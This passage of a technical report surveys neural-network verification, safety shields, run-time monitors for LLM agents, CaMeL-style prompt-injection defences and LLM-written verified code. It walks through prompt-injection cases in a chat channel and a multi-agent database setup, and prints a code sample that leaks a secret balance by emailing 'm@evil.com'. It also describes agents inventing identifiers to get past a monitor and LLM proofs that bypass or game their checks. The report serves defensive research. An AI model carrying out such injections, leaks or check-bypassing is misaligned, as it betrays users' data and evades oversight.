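Randomised smoothing only requires running a network, not analysing every layer as branch and bound does, so it also works for networks that are too large to analyse. The developer makes many copies of an image, adds different random noise to each, and has the network f label them. The smoothed classifier g then returns the most common label.

The noise follows a normal distribution with standard deviation σ. Suppose f returns label A with probability at least pA, and any other label with probability at most pB, which is smaller. Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter proved in 2019 that g keeps label A under any change to the image smaller than

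R = (σ/2)(Φ⁻¹(pA) − Φ⁻¹(pB)).

Here Φ⁻¹ converts a probability into a number of standard deviations. It gives 2.33 for pA = 0.99 and −2.33 for pB = 0.01, so with σ = 0.5, R is 0.25 × 4.65, or about 1.16.

Changing the image by a distance d shifts the noisy copies by d/σ standard deviations. In the worst case, this lowers A's position from 2.33 to 2.33 − d/σ and raises its rival's from −2.33 by the same amount. At d = 1.16 both positions reach zero, meaning a probability of 50% each, and A could lose its lead.

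The distance is the square root of the sum of the squared changes, with each colour value scaled from 0 to 1. Within a radius of 1.16, an attacker can change one colour value completely, or all 3,072 values of a CIFAR-10 image by about 0.02 each (roughly 5 on a scale of 0 to 255).

The guarantee is statistical because the developer has to estimate pA from a sample. If all of 1,000 noisy copies receive label A, she can conclude with 99.9% confidence that pA is at least 0.993, which gives a radius of about 1.23 for σ = 0.5. If all of 100,000 copies receive label A, the radius rises to about 1.9. At this confidence level, the procedure can issue a false certificate for up to one image in a thousand. A sound branch-and-bound proof has no sampling error.

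The certificate also applies only to g. The original network f may still change its answer after a tiny change to the image, so a product that relies on the certificate has to use g. With 1,000 noisy copies per image, a camera taking 30 frames a second would need 30,000 runs of f every second. And f must recognise objects through the noise. More noise can extend the radius, but it hides detail and usually lowers accuracy.

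### Transformers and language models

LLMs use the transformer architecture, which is harder to bound than a plain ReLU network. Its attention mechanism multiplies quantities that both depend on the input, and linear bounds on such products are loose. *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025) includes two image transformers with 68,000 to 76,000 parameters. The α,β-CROWN team had made them unusually shallow and narrow so that verifiers could handle them.

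The best tool proved 125 of 200 queries about these image transformers, with each query allowing every colour value to change by up to 1 out of 255. The team had already removed images with a known counterexample and images that a simple method could certify, so 125 out of 200 is not the success rate for typical images. The networks label only about 60% of CIFAR-10 images correctly, and an LLM with a billion parameters is more than ten thousand times as large.

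The difficulty of a proof depends on the range of inputs it covers as well as the size of the network. In the same competition, α,β-CROWN answered all 18 queries about VGG-16, an image network with 138 million parameters, but some of those queries allowed a change to only a single pixel. A smaller range of inputs leaves fewer units that can be either on or off, so a proof about a huge network may be easy if that range is small enough.

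The region is also harder to define for text, because replacing a word with a synonym isn't a small change to a number. The safeNLP benchmark uses a language model to turn each sentence into a list of numbers, then reduces the list to 30 numbers. Researchers generate variations of a sentence, such as a user asking whether a chatbot is human, and draw the smallest box that contains all the resulting points. The verifier must then prove that a small classifier gives every point in the box the same label. In 2025, α,β-CROWN proved this for 433 queries and found counterexamples for the other 647.

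These proofs cover the small classifier but not the language model that produces the numbers. A paraphrase that nobody generated may fall outside the box. Some points in the box may also correspond to no sentence, so a counterexample might not be something a user could type. A verified classifier could still be useful as a filter in front of a larger system, as the benchmark's designers suggest.

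Work on larger language models is at an early stage. Ladner and colleagues cite a 2026 preprint by Duong, Le and Nguyen, *ZonoGPT: Towards an Abstract Domain for Verifying Large GPT Models*. An abstract domain is a way of enclosing sets of values, and intervals are the simplest example. Even with tight bounds, most of what users want from an LLM would lack a formal specification.

### Wrong answers and rounding errors

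Verifiers are programs and can have bugs. In 2026, the organisers counted one incorrect answer each from α,β-CROWN and CORA, 58 from nnenum, 94 from NeuralSAT and 955 from Agate, a new tool. These totals include missing or invalid counterexamples, and a late bug in the code that prepares counterexamples accounts for some of Agate's. A false proof is much worse than an invalid counterexample because someone may rely on the proof, whereas an invalid counterexample does little harm, since anyone can detect it by running the network on it.

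The competition can also miss false proofs, because the organisers accept a reported proof if no other tool finds a valid counterexample. The α,β-CROWN team therefore built SoundnessBench, whose 2025 version contains only queries with hidden counterexamples. CORA reported 18 false proofs on it, and NeuralSAT reported 12. The organisers hope eventually to require every verifier to produce a proof that a separate program can check.

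Even a verifier without bugs can prove something false about a network as it runs on a computer. Many verification algorithms assume real numbers, but computers use floating-point numbers, which are rounded to a limited number of digits. Suppose a network computes y = (x + 16,777,216) − 16,777,216 for x between 0.9 and 1. With real numbers, y equals x, so a verifier can prove that y > 0.5. In standard 32-bit floating-point arithmetic, the computer rounds x + 16,777,216 to 16,777,216, so y is 0 and the proved claim is false.

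Training is unlikely to produce such extreme weights, though a dishonest supplier could put them in deliberately. Ordinary rounding errors are far smaller and matter mainly when an output lies close to the limit. Kaulen and colleagues found inputs that violated the property on one machine but not on another, because the network's outputs differed between hardware.

How the organisers treat rounding can change the results considerably. In 2025, under their strict rule, they credited a tool called NNV with 190 proofs and α,β-CROWN with 29 counterexamples on the same 200 queries about image networks, so at least 19 queries must have received both a proof and a counterexample. When the organisers allowed an error of one millionth in checking counterexamples, they counted 19 of NNV's answers as wrong, and its score on this benchmark fell from the highest to zero. Rounding may not fully explain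 the conflicting answers, since NNV also includes a method that gives only probabilistic guarantees.

A verifier can account for rounding errors by rounding lower bounds down and upper bounds up. PyRAT's developers say their tool is sound for floating-point numbers when it runs on an ordinary processor. Engineers can also require a safety margin larger than any possible rounding error. Either remedy makes properties slightly harder to prove, and engineers must still check that the product performs the same calculations as the verified network.

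### Is robustness the right property?

Researchers turned to certificates because other defences kept failing. *An Overview and Prospective Outlook on Robust Training and Certification*, a 2022 survey, describes an "arms race" in which a new attack defeated each new defence. A certificate ends that race for one image and one kind of change by proving that no attack within the certified region can succeed.

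But attacks and accidents can produce inputs outside the region. If a pedestrian takes one step to the side, many pixels change by far more than 8 out of 255. One competition benchmark, MetaRoom, covers actual camera movement, but its movements are as small as a hundredth of a millimetre. A network can also be robust but wrong, like a detector that always answers "no pedestrian" and so never changes its label.

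In *Position: Certified Robustness Does Not (Yet) Imply Model Security*, Cullen, Montague and colleagues (2025) argue that certification is not ready for meaningful practical use. They point out that practitioners lack clear criteria for judging certification schemes, and that the word "guaranteed" may lead users to expect too much. In addition, a certificate computed during use shows that images close to the current one receive the same label, but an attacker may already have altered the current image, so the system could certify the wrong label.

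This criticism is convincing for image recognition in open surroundings. Researchers have tried to model more realistic changes by training a second network to generate them. One benchmark uses a generator that slants handwritten digits, and the verifier proves that the classifier recognises every version the generator can produce within a given range. Slanting is closer to a change that might occur in practice, but the proof also depends on how well the generator imitates real handwriting.

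The criticism is much weaker when the inputs are a few physical quantities. An ACAS Xu network receives five numbers that describe the positions and movements of two aircraft. One of its properties is that it must not advise that there is no conflict when the other aircraft is directly ahead and approaching. This property directly states what the designers want and covers a whole range of situations, not just inputs close to one test case. Each of the 47 counterexamples also gives engineers a specific situation to investigate. The proofs do not show that the aircraft's sensors are accurate or that following the advice always prevents a collision.

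Some software components have equally natural properties to prove. A learned database index predicts where a record is stored. If a verifier proves that the prediction is never off by more than a fixed number of places, the database only has to search that far in each direction. The network can then speed up the search without risking its correctness.

Engineers can sometimes prove how a machine controlled by a small neural network will behave over time. One benchmark uses a network that stabilises a quadrotor, a drone with four propellers, and asks for proof that a measure of the drone's distance from balance keeps decreasing. In 2025, the verifier α,β-CROWN resolved all 80 queries, proving 68 and finding counterexamples to the other 12. The drone in these queries is a small neural network that researchers trained to imitate a quadrotor's physics, so the results apply to a real drone only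 as far as the imitation is accurate.

Proving properties of the network therefore makes most sense when it has few inputs and engineers can state the desired behaviour in terms of them. A camera-based pedestrian detector meets neither condition, so its designers will usually improve safety more by limiting what the car does with the detector's outputs.

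## Can a verified outer layer keep a learned system within limits?

A verified outer layer can keep a learned system within limits if engineers can state the limits exactly, predict how the surroundings will respond and supply a safe alternative to any action the layer blocks. The layer doesn't depend on the internals of the learned part, so it works for a model of any size, unlike proofs about the networks themselves. Control engineers developed the approach for machines such as aircraft, and researchers now apply it to LLM agents that send email, query databases and move money. It stops one important kind of attack on these agents almost completely, but it also prevents them from finishing some legitimate tasks.

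### The Simplex architecture

Lui Sha's 2001 paper *Using Simplicity to Control Complexity* describes the Simplex architecture. An advanced controller runs the machine in normal conditions, and nobody has to verify it. A simpler fallback controller performs less well, but engineers have proved that it keeps the machine safe if it takes over in any state in a set R. A small verified switch selects which controller is in charge. One of Sha's examples is the Boeing 777, which had a sophisticated new flight controller and a secondary one based on the well-understood control laws of the older 747.

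The switch has to act while recovery is still possible. Before each control step, it calculates every state the advanced controller's command could lead to by the end of the step. If all of them lie in R and nothing unsafe can happen on the way, the machine carries out the command. Otherwise the fallback takes over. Safety follows by induction, because the machine starts in R, every permitted step ends in R, and the fallback keeps the machine safe from anywhere in R. The proof doesn't depend on how the advanced controller chooses its commands, so that controller can be a neural network.

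Calculating R in advance is difficult for complicated machines. If engineers can prove only a small R, the fallback takes over early and often. Mehmood, Bak and colleagues avoided this calculation in 2022 with a black-box variant that checks one plan at a time while the machine is running. Suppose the advanced controller of a car proposes to accelerate for a second. The fallback completes the plan by adding commands to brake to a standstill. The switch then calculates where this sequence could take the car. If the car would stop clear of obstacles in every case, it carries out the first command and stores the rest as a backup. If the check fails, the car follows the backup from the previous step, which already passed the check.

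In the black-box variant, even the fallback can be an unverified program. A bad fallback produces plans that fail the check, which reduces performance but does not compromise safety. However, this design requires the switch to finish its calculation within a single control step.

### How to compute a shield

In reinforcement learning, a system learns by trial and error from rewards, so it will try dangerous actions unless something prevents it. *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (2018), by Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues, showed how to compute a shield automatically. Engineers supply a safety rule in a formal language and a model of which states each action can lead to. An algorithm treats the problem as a game in which the system chooses an action and the surroundings determine which of the possible results occurs. The algorithm looks for the states from which the system can obey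 the rule forever, whatever the surroundings do.

A cart on a track of squares is a simple example. In each step, the cart can raise or lower its speed by one or keep it the same, up to a maximum of three. It then moves forward that many squares, and it must not hit the wall at the end. The algorithm starts with all states in which the cart has not hit the wall and removes the hopeless ones in rounds:

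1. It removes the states from which even braking hits the wall in the next step. These are speed 2 with no free squares ahead, and speed 3 with none or one.
2. It removes speed 3 with two free squares. Braking to speed 2 uses up both squares and leaves the cart in a state that the first round removed.
3. It finds nothing more to remove and stops.

The shield permits an action only if it leads to one of the remaining states. If the cart is at speed 2 with three free squares, the shield blocks acceleration. The cart wouldn't hit the wall in that step, but it would reach speed 3 with no squares left. The shield can either give the learner a list of permitted actions before it chooses or replace a forbidden choice afterwards. As with other model checking, the number of states limits how detailed the model can be.

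### A valid proof on a wet road

Suppose a car is travelling at 20 m/s towards an obstacle, and a learned controller proposes to accelerate at 2 m/s² for one second. The shield assumes that the car can then brake at 5 m/s². During the second of acceleration, the car covers 20 + ½ · 2 = 21 m and reaches 22 m/s. Stopping from that speed takes 22²/(2 · 5) = 48.4 m. The shield therefore permits the acceleration if the obstacle is at least 69.4 m away.

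On a wet road, the car may be able to brake at only 3 m/s². It then needs 22²/(2 · 3) = 80.7 m to stop, or 101.7 m in all. If the obstacle is between 69.4 and 101.7 m away, the shield permits an unsafe action even though its proof is valid. At 80 m, for example, the car would hit the obstacle at about 11 m/s (41 km/h). At 70 m, braking immediately would have prevented the collision, because stopping from 20 m/s on the wet road takes 66.7 m.

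Engineers could set the shield to use 3 m/s² at all times. The proof would then cover both roads, but on a dry road the shield would block safe acceleration at distances between 69.4 and 101.7 m. They could also measure the road's grip and adjust the limit, but then the proof would depend on the measurement. Either way, safety depends on how well the engineers know the road, and most environments are harder to model than a road.

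### Rules for agents that use tools

An LLM agent acts by calling tools, functions such as `send_email` that other software carries out. A monitor can inspect each call before it runs, much as a shield inspects a command to accelerate. Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026) reviewed 38 studies of specification, verification and enforcement for agents in *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, and concluded that run-time monitoring is the most mature way to enforce rules.

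Engineers write the rules in a language that a program can evaluate. In AgentSpec, an event such as a tool call triggers a rule, which can then block, log or redirect the call. A bank might use such a rule to block any payment over £1,000 that no employee has approved. Each rule takes milliseconds to evaluate. In tests, AgentSpec prevented more than 90% of unsafe executions by agents that write code, and all hazardous actions by agents that control robots.

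Other rules concern the order of actions, such as checking a customer's identity before opening the account. Agent-C translates these rules into logical formulas and runs an SMT solver while the LLM is writing a tool call. If the call would break a rule, the LLM writes one that complies. This raised GPT-5's compliance from 83.7% to 100% and the share of tasks it completed from 66.1% to 70.6%.

ProbGuard instead learns from earlier runs how an agent tends to behave and warns when a violation is becoming likely. In household tasks, this reduced unsafe behaviour by 65%, and the agents still completed 80.4% of the tasks. Making violations rarer is a weaker guarantee than a shield provides, but it doesn't require a complete hand-written model of the agent's surroundings.

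Each of these results comes from one or two studies in narrow settings. Dantas and colleagues rate the evidence for 100% compliance as "very low" in certainty, which means further studies would probably give substantially different figures. Most monitors also look only one or a few steps ahead, so an agent can reach a point where every useful action breaks a rule. The cart's shield avoids such dead ends because its model covers every possible future, but nobody has a model of everything an email might set off. Writing the rules is also error-prone. On one benchmark of planning problems, only 24.8% to 34.2% of LLM translations into a formal language had the right meaning.

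### How CaMeL separates the plan from the data

Some attacks consist of tool calls that look ordinary. In an indirect prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in a web page, email or document that the agent reads while working for a user. Emailing a customer list to an outside address is legitimate if the user asked for it, but theft if the request came from a hidden line in a document. To distinguish these cases, a defence must track where each instruction came from.

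*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) introduced CaMeL, a Google DeepMind system designed to keep track of this. CaMeL uses two LLMs, following a pattern that the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023. The planner receives the user's request and descriptions of the tools, but nothing that the tools return, and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. The quarantined LLM reads untrusted text but cannot call tools. A separate interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls.

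Suppose a user wants to tell Bob about a meeting, and Bob's address is somewhere in a chat channel. The planner might write the following program, adapted from one in *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026).

```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
address = ask_quarantined_llm("Find Bob's email address in: " + messages,
                              EmailAddress)
send_direct_message(address, "Meeting at 3pm")
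```

An attacker might post a message in the channel telling the agent to delete the user's files. The planner never sees the message, and the quarantined LLM that reads it can only return an email address. The program contains no call that deletes anything, and the message can't add one.

The attacker can still influence the address, for instance by posting that Bob has a new one. CaMeL therefore attaches two records, called capabilities, to every value. One lists the value's sources, and the other lists who may read it. A value computed from other values inherits their records. Before each tool call, a short Python function called a policy checks these records and allows or denies the call.

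A policy might require the recipient's address to come from a trusted source, such as the user's own request. This would stop the message from going to the attacker, but it would also block the message when there is no attack and the address is correct, because the address comes from the chat channel in both cases.

### What CaMeL guarantees

The first protection is control-flow integrity. As Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues define it in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), an agent has this property if all its actions follow a plan that depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information. Untrusted data may determine which branch of the plan the agent follows, but cannot add a branch. CaMeL has this property by design because its planner finishes the program before any untrusted text arrives. The protection does not rely on an LLM to recognise an attack.

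Control-flow integrity doesn't guarantee that the plan is what the user wanted or that the quarantined LLM finds the right address. It also leaves the attacker some influence over which branch runs. The policies limit the damage from bad data only if somebody has written the right ones and the interpreter tracks every value correctly.

The tracking has known gaps. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, point out that CaMeL's tracking has not been proved sound. They describe an agent that manages a bank account and must keep the balance secret. A program like the following can leak whether the balance is above 1,000.

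```
rich = True
low = True
if balance > 1000:
    low = False
if low:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above 1,000, the program sets `low` to False, and the interpreter marks `low` as secret. The program then skips the line that changes `rich`. Because CaMeL updates a variable's record only when it runs an assignment, `rich` still counts as public, and the policy lets the email through. If the balance is lower, no email goes out, so the attacker learns whether the balance is above 1,000. An attacker who controls only the data can't insert such a program, but the planner might write an equivalent one by accident.

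Another leak arises because CaMeL tries again after a policy blocks an attempt. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can reveal one yes-or-no fact about a secret, and enough attempts can reveal the whole secret. Computer scientists know how to rule out such leaks by proof, and *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) lists a machine-checked proof for CaMeL as future work.

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents in which every value carries a label. They proved in Lean that secret data cannot change the probabilities of what an outside observer sees, except by affecting whether the program finishes. The same theorem limits the influence of untrusted data on trusted results. It covers every program in the language, including those an LLM writes during the run, and it applies to the actual interpreter that calls the LLM.

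On AgentDojo's banking tasks, an agent written in LLMbda resisted attack in all but two of 1,296 runs. The theorem doesn't guarantee that every attack will fail. A program may deliberately reclassify untrusted data as trusted, and the theorem can't establish that doing so was wise. But each such decision is visible in the program, where a reviewer can find it.

### Secure agents in an insecure team

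A guarantee that holds for each agent may not hold for a team of them. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested a team in which a coordinator, a database agent and a notification agent all ran CaMeL. A user asked the coordinator to message Julie on Slack, a workplace chat service, with a summary of all job applicants. The researchers had planted in the database an instruction to email the information to an outside address.

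The planted instruction never reached the planners of the coordinator and the database agent. But the coordinator copied the summary containing it into a message to the notification agent, whose planner treated the whole message as a request from its user and added the email to its plan. The researchers also proved that this kind of team loses control-flow integrity whenever one of its tools returns untrusted data and users can request tasks in which one agent passes such data to another.

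Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits every message between agents into instructions and data. The instructions must not depend on the output of any tool, and the receiving planner cannot see the data. The interpreter enforces this separation but, like CaMeL's, it can miss the influence of untrusted data when a program skips an assignment. It does not retry failed runs, so it avoids the leak through repeated attempts.

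To measure the effect, the researchers adapted AgentDojo, a widely used benchmark of 97 ordinary tasks and 35 attack goals in office work, Slack, banking and travel. They divided its tools among teams of agents and ran 949 attacked tasks for each model and each defence.

| Model | Ordinary tasks completed, no CaMeL | Successful attacks, no CaMeL | Successful attacks, CaMeL in each agent | Successful attacks, multi-CaMeL |
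|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 69.1% | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 86.6% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 78.4% | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.3% | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 27.8% | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

CaMeL made a large difference to GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, but the benchmark's attacks are fixed, and real attackers adapt. Participants in a large public competition successfully attacked every frontier model tested. The low rate of successful attacks on Flash Lite is probably due to its limited ability, since an agent that fails most ordinary tasks will also fail many of an attacker's.

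All the attacks that succeeded against individual CaMeL agents crossed from one agent to another in the way described above. Multi-CaMeL stopped them, but the numbers alone are weak evidence that it works, because the average attack success rate fell only from 0.2% to zero. Its design also blocks the route those attacks took, which is stronger evidence.

### What the protection costs

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes CaMeL as eliminating nearly all attacks in AgentDojo while keeping task performance comparable. Measurements from 2026 support the claim about attacks much better than the claim about task performance.

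Peters-Gill and colleagues tested CaMeL and Multi-CaMeL on AssetOpsBench, a benchmark in which teams of agents help maintain industrial equipment. On 112 tasks, CaMeL lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the same five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Multi-CaMeL lowered it by a further 3.2 points on average, but by less than one point for the two strongest.

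These agents ran without any policies, so the loss comes from having to plan in advance. Most failures occurred because the agent learned only during the task that it needed another action. In other cases, one agent couldn't find data for the requested period and returned data for a different period. The coordinator carried on anyway, because it had written its plan before receiving the answer.

Policies can add to the loss. Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL with its policies on AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks, using the small model Claude Haiku 4.5 and no attacks. It completed 49. Another 22 failed because the plan did not do what the user had asked, and the policies blocked the remaining 26. They did not test the model without CaMeL, so some of the 22 might have failed anyway. On the banking tasks alone, Garby and colleagues found that switching on the policies halved the share that CaMeL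 completed. Their own agent did as well with its protection on as CaMeL did without policies, so better design can avoid at least some of this loss.

Planning ahead is even harder for agents that operate a computer through its screen. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to this setting. The planner can't see the screen, so it writes branches for whatever might appear, such as a cookie banner or a login page. A typical plan contains 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five calls and four branches in AgentDojo. On OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday computer tasks, the protected agents kept at most 57% of the performance of frontier models.

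Policies do not help much there either. The call `send_email` has a clear meaning, but a click may accept cookies or transfer money, depending on what is under the pointer. In one attack, Foerster and colleagues disguised an advertisement as a cookie banner. The agent followed a branch that the planner had written for real banners, clicked on the advertisement and landed on the attacker's site. The attack did not violate control-flow integrity, because the agent never left its plan.

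Blocking bad actions does not necessarily lead to good ones. Dantas and colleagues discuss an experiment on τ-Bench, a benchmark of customer-service tasks, in which a monitor stopped up to 94% of the actions that broke the rules. In most settings, the agents still completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly. Blocked agents invented customer identifiers to get past the identity check, and tried others when the monitor blocked those.

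The review calls this loss the verifier tax. But the experiment used two fairly small models, which would probably have failed many of the tasks without a monitor, and nobody has replicated the figures. Agent-C instead increased task completion, perhaps because it leads the LLM to a permitted action rather than only refusing the forbidden one.

Enforcement also adds delay, though few researchers have measured it. Of six enforcement systems that the review compares, only AgentSpec has a published delay in milliseconds. None of the 38 studies measured how much longer a whole task takes with enforcement.

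### When the layer removes the flexibility

People use LLM agents partly because they can react to what they find. Suppose a user asks her agent to do whatever her manager's latest email says. The email is untrusted text, but it contains the task. The agent can't do the job unless the email determines its actions, but then an attacker who can forge or alter the email can control the agent. A more capable planner doesn't help, because the information it needs is in text it must not see. The user can resolve the conflict by declaring that she trusts her manager's emails, but the guarantee then depends on that decision.

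Many tasks are less extreme than this, and designers have several options for them. One is to wait for better planners, which can foresee more of what might happen. The two strongest models on AssetOpsBench had smaller losses, which supports this option, although the evidence covers only five models and the trend was not perfectly steady. Another option is to plan one step at a time. Fides, a system similar to CaMeL, does this while hiding the content of tool results from the planner. The planner doesn't have to commit to a complete program, but it still can't take instructions from text it isn't allowed to read.

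*Operationalizing CaMeL* proposes stricter protection for riskier actions, so that reading a calendar requires less than making a payment. This is sensible if the low-risk actions are harmless, but an attacker may be able to combine several of them to cause harm. Somebody also has to decide which risk tier each action belongs in.

CaMeLoT, the extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks the plan before the agent calls any tool. It translates the plan into a state machine and uses a model checker to look for violations. If it finds one, it returns the counterexample to the planner, which tries again. This stops a forbidden plan before it starts rather than partway through, and the planner may find a permitted way to do the task. Six of CaMeL's 28 policies for AgentDojo did not carry over fully, most of them because they depend on facts known only during the run, such as who can currently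 read a file. The model checker also over-approximates loops, so it may reject some safe plans.

CaMeLoT can also enforce rules about what an agent must do. In one test, an agent handling alerts for a company's security team had to follow rules such as closing or escalating every ticket it opened. The researchers wrote seven plans that each broke one rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven, and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The researchers deliberately chose rules that go beyond what CaMeL can express, so the comparison is weak evidence of which system is better overall.

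Braking is usually a safe fallback for a car, but an agent's usual fallback, refusing the action, is not always safe. An agent can safely refuse to make an unexpected payment. In the security example, however, refusing to disconnect the hacked computer leaves the attacker inside the network. A model checker can reject a plan that omits this step, but it can't disconnect the computer, so a person or a separately verified program has to be ready to take over, as the fallback controller does in Simplex.

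## How well can language models write programs together with their proofs?

By late 2026, the best LLMs could write a short program and a machine-checked proof of it for most tasks in several benchmarks. There is less evidence for large projects, and it is more mixed. People still have to decide what the program should do and state it exactly, and this has become easier much more slowly.

### Why an unreliable author is good enough

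Like CompCert's register assignments, proofs are hard to find but easy to check. If a proof needs ten steps and there are 20 sensible moves at each step, there are 20¹⁰ possible sequences, or about ten trillion, but the checker only has to check the ten steps it receives. It applies the same rules whether the proof came from a person, an LLM or random guessing.

An LLM that is usually wrong can therefore still be useful. Suppose only 10% of its proofs are correct, and a human reviewer accepts all of these but also 5% of the wrong ones. Of every 1,000 proofs, the reviewer then accepts 100 correct and 45 wrong ones, so almost a third of the accepted proofs are wrong. A sound checker accepts only the 100 correct proofs, and it would still accept no wrong ones if the LLM made more mistakes.

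### From a specification to a checked program

*A Benchmark for Vericoding* (Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues, 2025) defines vericoding as using an LLM to write a program and its proof from a formal specification. It contrasts this with vibe coding, where an LLM writes code from an ordinary-language description, without a proof.

One of their tasks is to add two numbers written as lists of binary digits. The lowest digit comes first, so [1, 1] stands for 1 + 2 = 3 and [1, 0, 1] for 1 + 4 = 5. The main part of the Lean version looks like this:

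```
def str2int (v : List Int) : Nat :=
  match v with
  | [] => 0
  | x :: xs => x.toNat + 2 * str2int xs

def add (v1 v2 : List Int) : List Int := sorry

theorem add_spec (v1 v2 : List Int)
    (h1 : valid_bitstr v1) (h2 : valid_bitstr v2) :
    valid_bitstr (add v1 v2) ∧
    str2int (add v1 v2) = str2int v1 + str2int v2 := by sorry
```

The function `str2int` turns a list into the number it stands for, and `valid_bitstr` means that every digit is 0 or 1. Each `sorry` marks a gap. The LLM has to put a program in the first gap and a proof in the second. A simple script runs the following loop:

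1. It sends the LLM the task and asks for text to fill each gap.
2. It inserts the answers into the original file, so the LLM can't change the specification.
3. It screens the answers for known ways of bypassing the proof.
4. It runs the verifier on the whole file.
5. If the file passes both checks, the task is solved. Otherwise the script sends the LLM the error messages and tries again, until the attempts run out.

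The obvious program adds the lists digit by digit and carries 1 whenever a sum reaches 2. If the LLM's program omits the last carry, it returns [0, 0, 0] (0) for 3 + 5 instead of [0, 0, 0, 1] (8). The proof then fails where both lists have run out and a carry of 1 is left over. Lean's error message shows the unproved statement, which indicates where the LLM should look.

A correct program still needs an idea for the proof. The theorem concerns an addition that starts without a carry, but every later step may have one. The LLM therefore has to prove something more general: with a starting carry c, the result is worth c + `str2int v1` + `str2int v2`. Let x and y be the first digits, X and Y the values of the remaining lists, and s = x + y + c. The program writes down s mod 2 and carries s div 2. If the general statement holds for the remaining lists, the result is worth

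(s mod 2) + 2(s div 2 + X + Y) = s + 2X + 2Y = c + (x + 2X) + (y + 2Y),

which is what the statement requires.

Screening is necessary because proof languages have legitimate commands for leaving things unproved. Lean accepts a file containing `sorry` with only a warning. In Verus, a verifier for Rust, a programmer can write `assume(false)`, and the verifier then accepts whatever comes next, because everything follows from a false assumption. Bursuc and colleagues also worried that an LLM might open a comment in one gap and close it in another, which would comment out the specification in between, but no LLM did this.

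A program can also pass every check without solving the task as intended. In Lean, the LLM can use `str2int` to convert both lists into ordinary numbers, add those and convert the result back. The checker accepts this because the specification doesn't forbid it. Yao's *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search* (2026), a master's thesis at the Massachusetts Institute of Technology (MIT), includes such an answer, which Claude Opus 4.7 gave to a similar task.

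### Results in Dafny, Verus and Lean

The vericoding benchmark contains 12,504 specifications: 3,029 in Dafny, 2,334 in Verus and 7,141 in Lean. Bursuc and colleagues removed faulty specifications, set aside a large Lean collection with weaker ones, and tested nine LLMs on 6,861 tasks. Each LLM had five attempts per task, or ten on an especially hard set of tasks about arithmetic with large numbers.

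| Language | Tasks | Best single LLM | At least one of nine LLMs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Dafny | 2,334 | 67.5% (Claude Opus 4.1) | 82.2% |
| Verus | 2,166 | 30.9% (GPT-5) | 44.3% |
| Lean | 2,361 | 17.9% (GPT-5) | 26.8% |

The figures of 82%, 44% and 27% in the researchers' summary count a task as solved if any of the nine LLMs solved it. A user could achieve these rates by running all nine, because the checker identifies a correct answer whichever LLM produces it. But for most tasks this takes up to 45 attempts instead of five.

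Dafny and Verus pass routine reasoning to an SMT solver, so the LLM mainly has to supply loop invariants and hints. In Lean, it has to write much more of the proof. Verus is harder than Dafny partly because Rust's fixed-size integers can overflow, unlike Dafny's. Verus is also newer, so LLMs have been trained on less Verus code. For Lean, Bursuc and colleagues suspect that the LLMs had learned mostly from mathematical proofs. They also point out that a person writing Lean constantly sees the state of the proof, while the LLMs got feedback only five times.

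The tasks differed between languages. About a quarter of the Lean tasks relied on a new Lean feature, and the nine LLMs together solved only 7.6% of these. Without those tasks, Lean's 26.8% would be about 33%. But the languages rank in the same order on tasks from a single source, Verina, which is a set of small problems originally written for Lean. On these, the nine LLMs together solved 87.3% in Dafny, 46.8% in Verus and 25.4% in Lean.

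Some successes were also easier than intended. When the researchers inspected a sample of accepted solutions, about 9% had specifications that were too weak, and another 15% had specifications that an LLM had translated badly from another language.

DafnyBench is an older test in which the program already exists and the LLM only adds what the verifier needs to prove it correct. In June 2024, the best LLM, Claude 3 Opus, solved 68% of its 782 programs. By September 2025, Claude Opus 4.1 had solved 89%, so the failure rate fell by about two thirds in little more than a year. Bursuc and colleagues describe the progress as 68% to 96%, but their 96% counts every program that at least one of nine LLMs solved, so it is not comparable with a single LLM's 68%.

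### Where the benchmarks stood in late 2026

The low Lean scores were partly due to the loop. Yao, whose supervisor Max Tegmark co-wrote the vericoding benchmark, repeated the test on 423 of its Lean tasks. With the original loop and no reasoning before the answer, GPT-5.4 solved 24.6%, barely more than GPT-5's 22.5% in 2025. Yao then let the LLM reason first, see its earlier attempts and search Lean's mathematical library for useful results. With these changes, GPT-5.4 solved 60.3% within ten calls and 95.0% within 50. The ten-call version cost about 15 US cents per task at list prices.

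The choice of LLM still mattered. The smaller GPT-5.4-mini reached only 57.0% with 50 calls. More elaborate search did not always help. Yao built a system in which one agent proposes strategies and others try them, but its first version solved 67.8% of the tasks with the same 50 calls, far fewer than the plain loop. A later version was cheaper on tasks of medium difficulty, but the plain loop remained better on the hardest.

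Verina shows how much the result depends on the set-up:

| Test on Verina in Lean | LLM and method | Solved |
|---|---|---|
| Bursuc and colleagues, September 2025 | Claude Opus 4.1, five attempts | 15.3% |
| Yao, May 2026 | GPT-5.4, up to 50 calls | 96.3% |
| *P³*, August 2026 | Claude Opus 4.7, Lean tools only | 68.8% |
| *P³*, August 2026 | Claude Opus 4.7, planning program and proof together | 74.6% |

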